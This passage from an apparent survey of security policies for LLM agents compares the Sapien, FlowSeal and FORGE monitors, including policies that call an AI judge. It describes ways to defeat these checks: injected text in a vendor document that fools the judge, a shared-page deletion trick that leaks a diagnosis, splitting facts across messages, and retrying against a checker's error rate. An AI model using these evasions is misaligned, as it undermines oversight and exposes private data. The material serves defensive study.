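A very general tool causes a similar problem even if the monitor intercepts every call. The arguments of `send_money(recipient, amount)` show what the call will do, but the argument of `run_python(source)` is a whole program, and a rule about arguments can't determine what an arbitrary program will do. Tiffany and colleagues therefore denied Toolathlon's Python tool to every agent in their tests, and required Sapien's policies to restrict terminal commands, for instance to the search program `grep`. Their results don't cover an agent that can run any code it writes.

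Developers can give the agent narrower tools or add controls beneath it. Shim and colleagues suggest monitoring file and network operations in the operating system, which would catch a tool that reads or writes data directly. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* includes the operating system and sandbox among the components that must work correctly for the guarantees to hold. The rules at that level may well be lists again, such as a list of servers the agent's machine may contact.

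### Judgements of meaning inside a policy

If a harm depends on meaning, a policy could include a judgement of meaning, which in practice has to come from a person or a language model. Sapien's policies can call a function, `verify_with_ai`, that puts a yes-or-no question to a model. In slightly simplified form, a policy for Ana's request might be:

```
read_file(path="vendor.pdf")@doc .
send_email(to="ana@firm.example",
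           body=PREDICATE(is_faithful))

def is_faithful(body):
    return verify_with_ai(
        "Is this a faithful summary of the document?",
        doc.result, body)
```

The judge receives only the document, the email and the question, not the rest of the run, so an attacker has fewer places to put text that might sway it. The vendor's document is still one of those places, and a line planted there could claim that a faithful summary leaves out the price clause.

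If this fools the judge, Ana gets the bad summary. But the rest of the policy still holds, so the agent can only read one document and send one email to Ana. A condition that relies on a judge can only narrow what the policy allows, so a wrong "yes" loses only the protection that condition added. Sapien gives up its deterministic guarantee for that condition and keeps it for the others. In their security test, Tiffany and colleagues assumed that every such judge had been fooled. The policies' results therefore do not depend on the judges, and the test provides no evidence of how well the judges resist being fooled.

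A judge can block useful work by wrongly rejecting an action. In one task, the user wanted to update a standing order for the rent, but the bank's records listed it as a one-time payment. The judge read the request too literally and rejected the update. The policies called a judge an average of 0.6 times per AgentDojo task, which added 1.4 to 3.5 seconds per task, depending on the model.

FlowSeal, Shim and colleagues' system for protecting records such as Mark's diagnosis, relies on a separate model's judgement to let messages through to unknown recipients. This model, the content checker, compares each message with the protected records and returns either SAFE or BLOCKED. The system's confidentiality theorem excludes cases in which the checker wrongly returns SAFE, so a wrong approval leaks protected information. In Sapien, the surrounding rules would still limit the damage from a wrong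 approval.

The checker was replaced with a fixed answer to measure how much depends on it. The attacker in this test invited the agent to fill in its part of a shared page, so that the disclosure looked like ordinary teamwork.

| Content checker | Private items leaked | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Working normally | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Always refuses | 1.3% | 0% |
| Always approves | 24.9% | 79.4% |

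The version that always refused completed nothing because every recipient was unknown and the data owners ignored all requests for consent, so its zero completion rate partly reflects the set-up. Wrong approvals can't explain the 1.3%, since the checker approved nothing. The model that scored the leaks may have made some mistakes.

The judgement does make it possible to recognise disclosures that contain no private text. In another attack, Emily makes a shared page of true and false notes about Mark's health and asks Jane's agent to delete the entries that don't match its records. The agent writes nothing about Mark, but the remaining entries are the true ones. This attack obtained 75.6% of the private items against a defence that relied on detailed prompt instructions, and 2.3% against FlowSeal. A strict flow rule could also stop the deletions, because they depend on the diagnosis, but it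 would stop Jane's harmless edits to the page as well.

Shim and colleagues say that the checker mainly fails on paraphrases, and that it sometimes blocks a message that mentions a record without revealing its contents. They also suggest that an attacker could split one fact among several messages that would each pass the check. FlowSeal can be too cautious even when the owner would consent. In a test where sharing was the right outcome, it shared 32.7% of the records, compared with 61–86% for the other defences, because its agent asked for consent less often.

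A small error rate matters more when an attacker can keep trying. If a checker wrongly approved 2% of attempts and its errors were independent, the chance of at least one leak in 50 attempts would be

1 − 0.98⁵⁰ ≈ 64%

Errors on similar messages are unlikely to be independent, so this is only a rough guide. A deterministic rule that refuses a request the first time will also refuse it the fiftieth time.

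Judgements are even riskier when they change labels. Costa and colleagues mention that a system might relabel a document as trusted after an injection classifier has processed it, but warn against weakening the guarantees too much. If the classifier misses the instruction in the vendor's document, every later rule treats the vendor's text as trusted, including rules for calls that the classifier never examined.

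FORGE leaves the choice to the author of the policy. According to Palumbo and colleagues, its rules can call a classifier as an outside function, and the effect of an error depends on the rule that contains it:

```
Deny(a)  :- SummaryEmail(a), not Faithful(a).
Allow(a) :- ExternalSend(a), Harmless(a).
```

An attacker who fools `Faithful` avoids one refusal, but all the other rules still apply. Fooling `Harmless` gains the attacker a permission if the policy refuses calls by default and no `Deny` rule matches. Wherever possible, a cautious author would therefore use classifiers only to refuse calls.

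The table below compares what well-written rules of each kind can do about these hazards.

| Hazard | Action lists | Flow rules | Invariants | Judgements of meaning |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| False content sent to the right person | No help | Mark the source, or block all untrusted text | Help if code can compare the content with a reliable record | Can catch it, but an attacker may fool the judge |
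| Poor decision on trusted data | Help only by withholding the tool | No help from integrity labels | Limit the damage or require confirmation | May catch obvious mistakes |
| Harmful request from the user | Help only by withholding the tool | Reader rules restrict the user; integrity rules do not | Caps and approvals restrict the user | May recognise the harm, as may the agent's own model |
| Misleading answer | No help | Can restrict the sources of the answer | Little help | May catch it if the judge has the facts |
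| Permitted disclosures that combine | No help | No help if each disclosure is allowed | Block combinations that somebody has listed | May catch them if the judge has all the pieces |
| Model that errs or pursues its own aim | Limit the available actions | Reader rules hold; integrity rules may find nothing wrong | Hold whatever the model's reasons | Help if the judge doesn't share the fault |
| Action outside the monitored channels | No help | No help | No help | No help |
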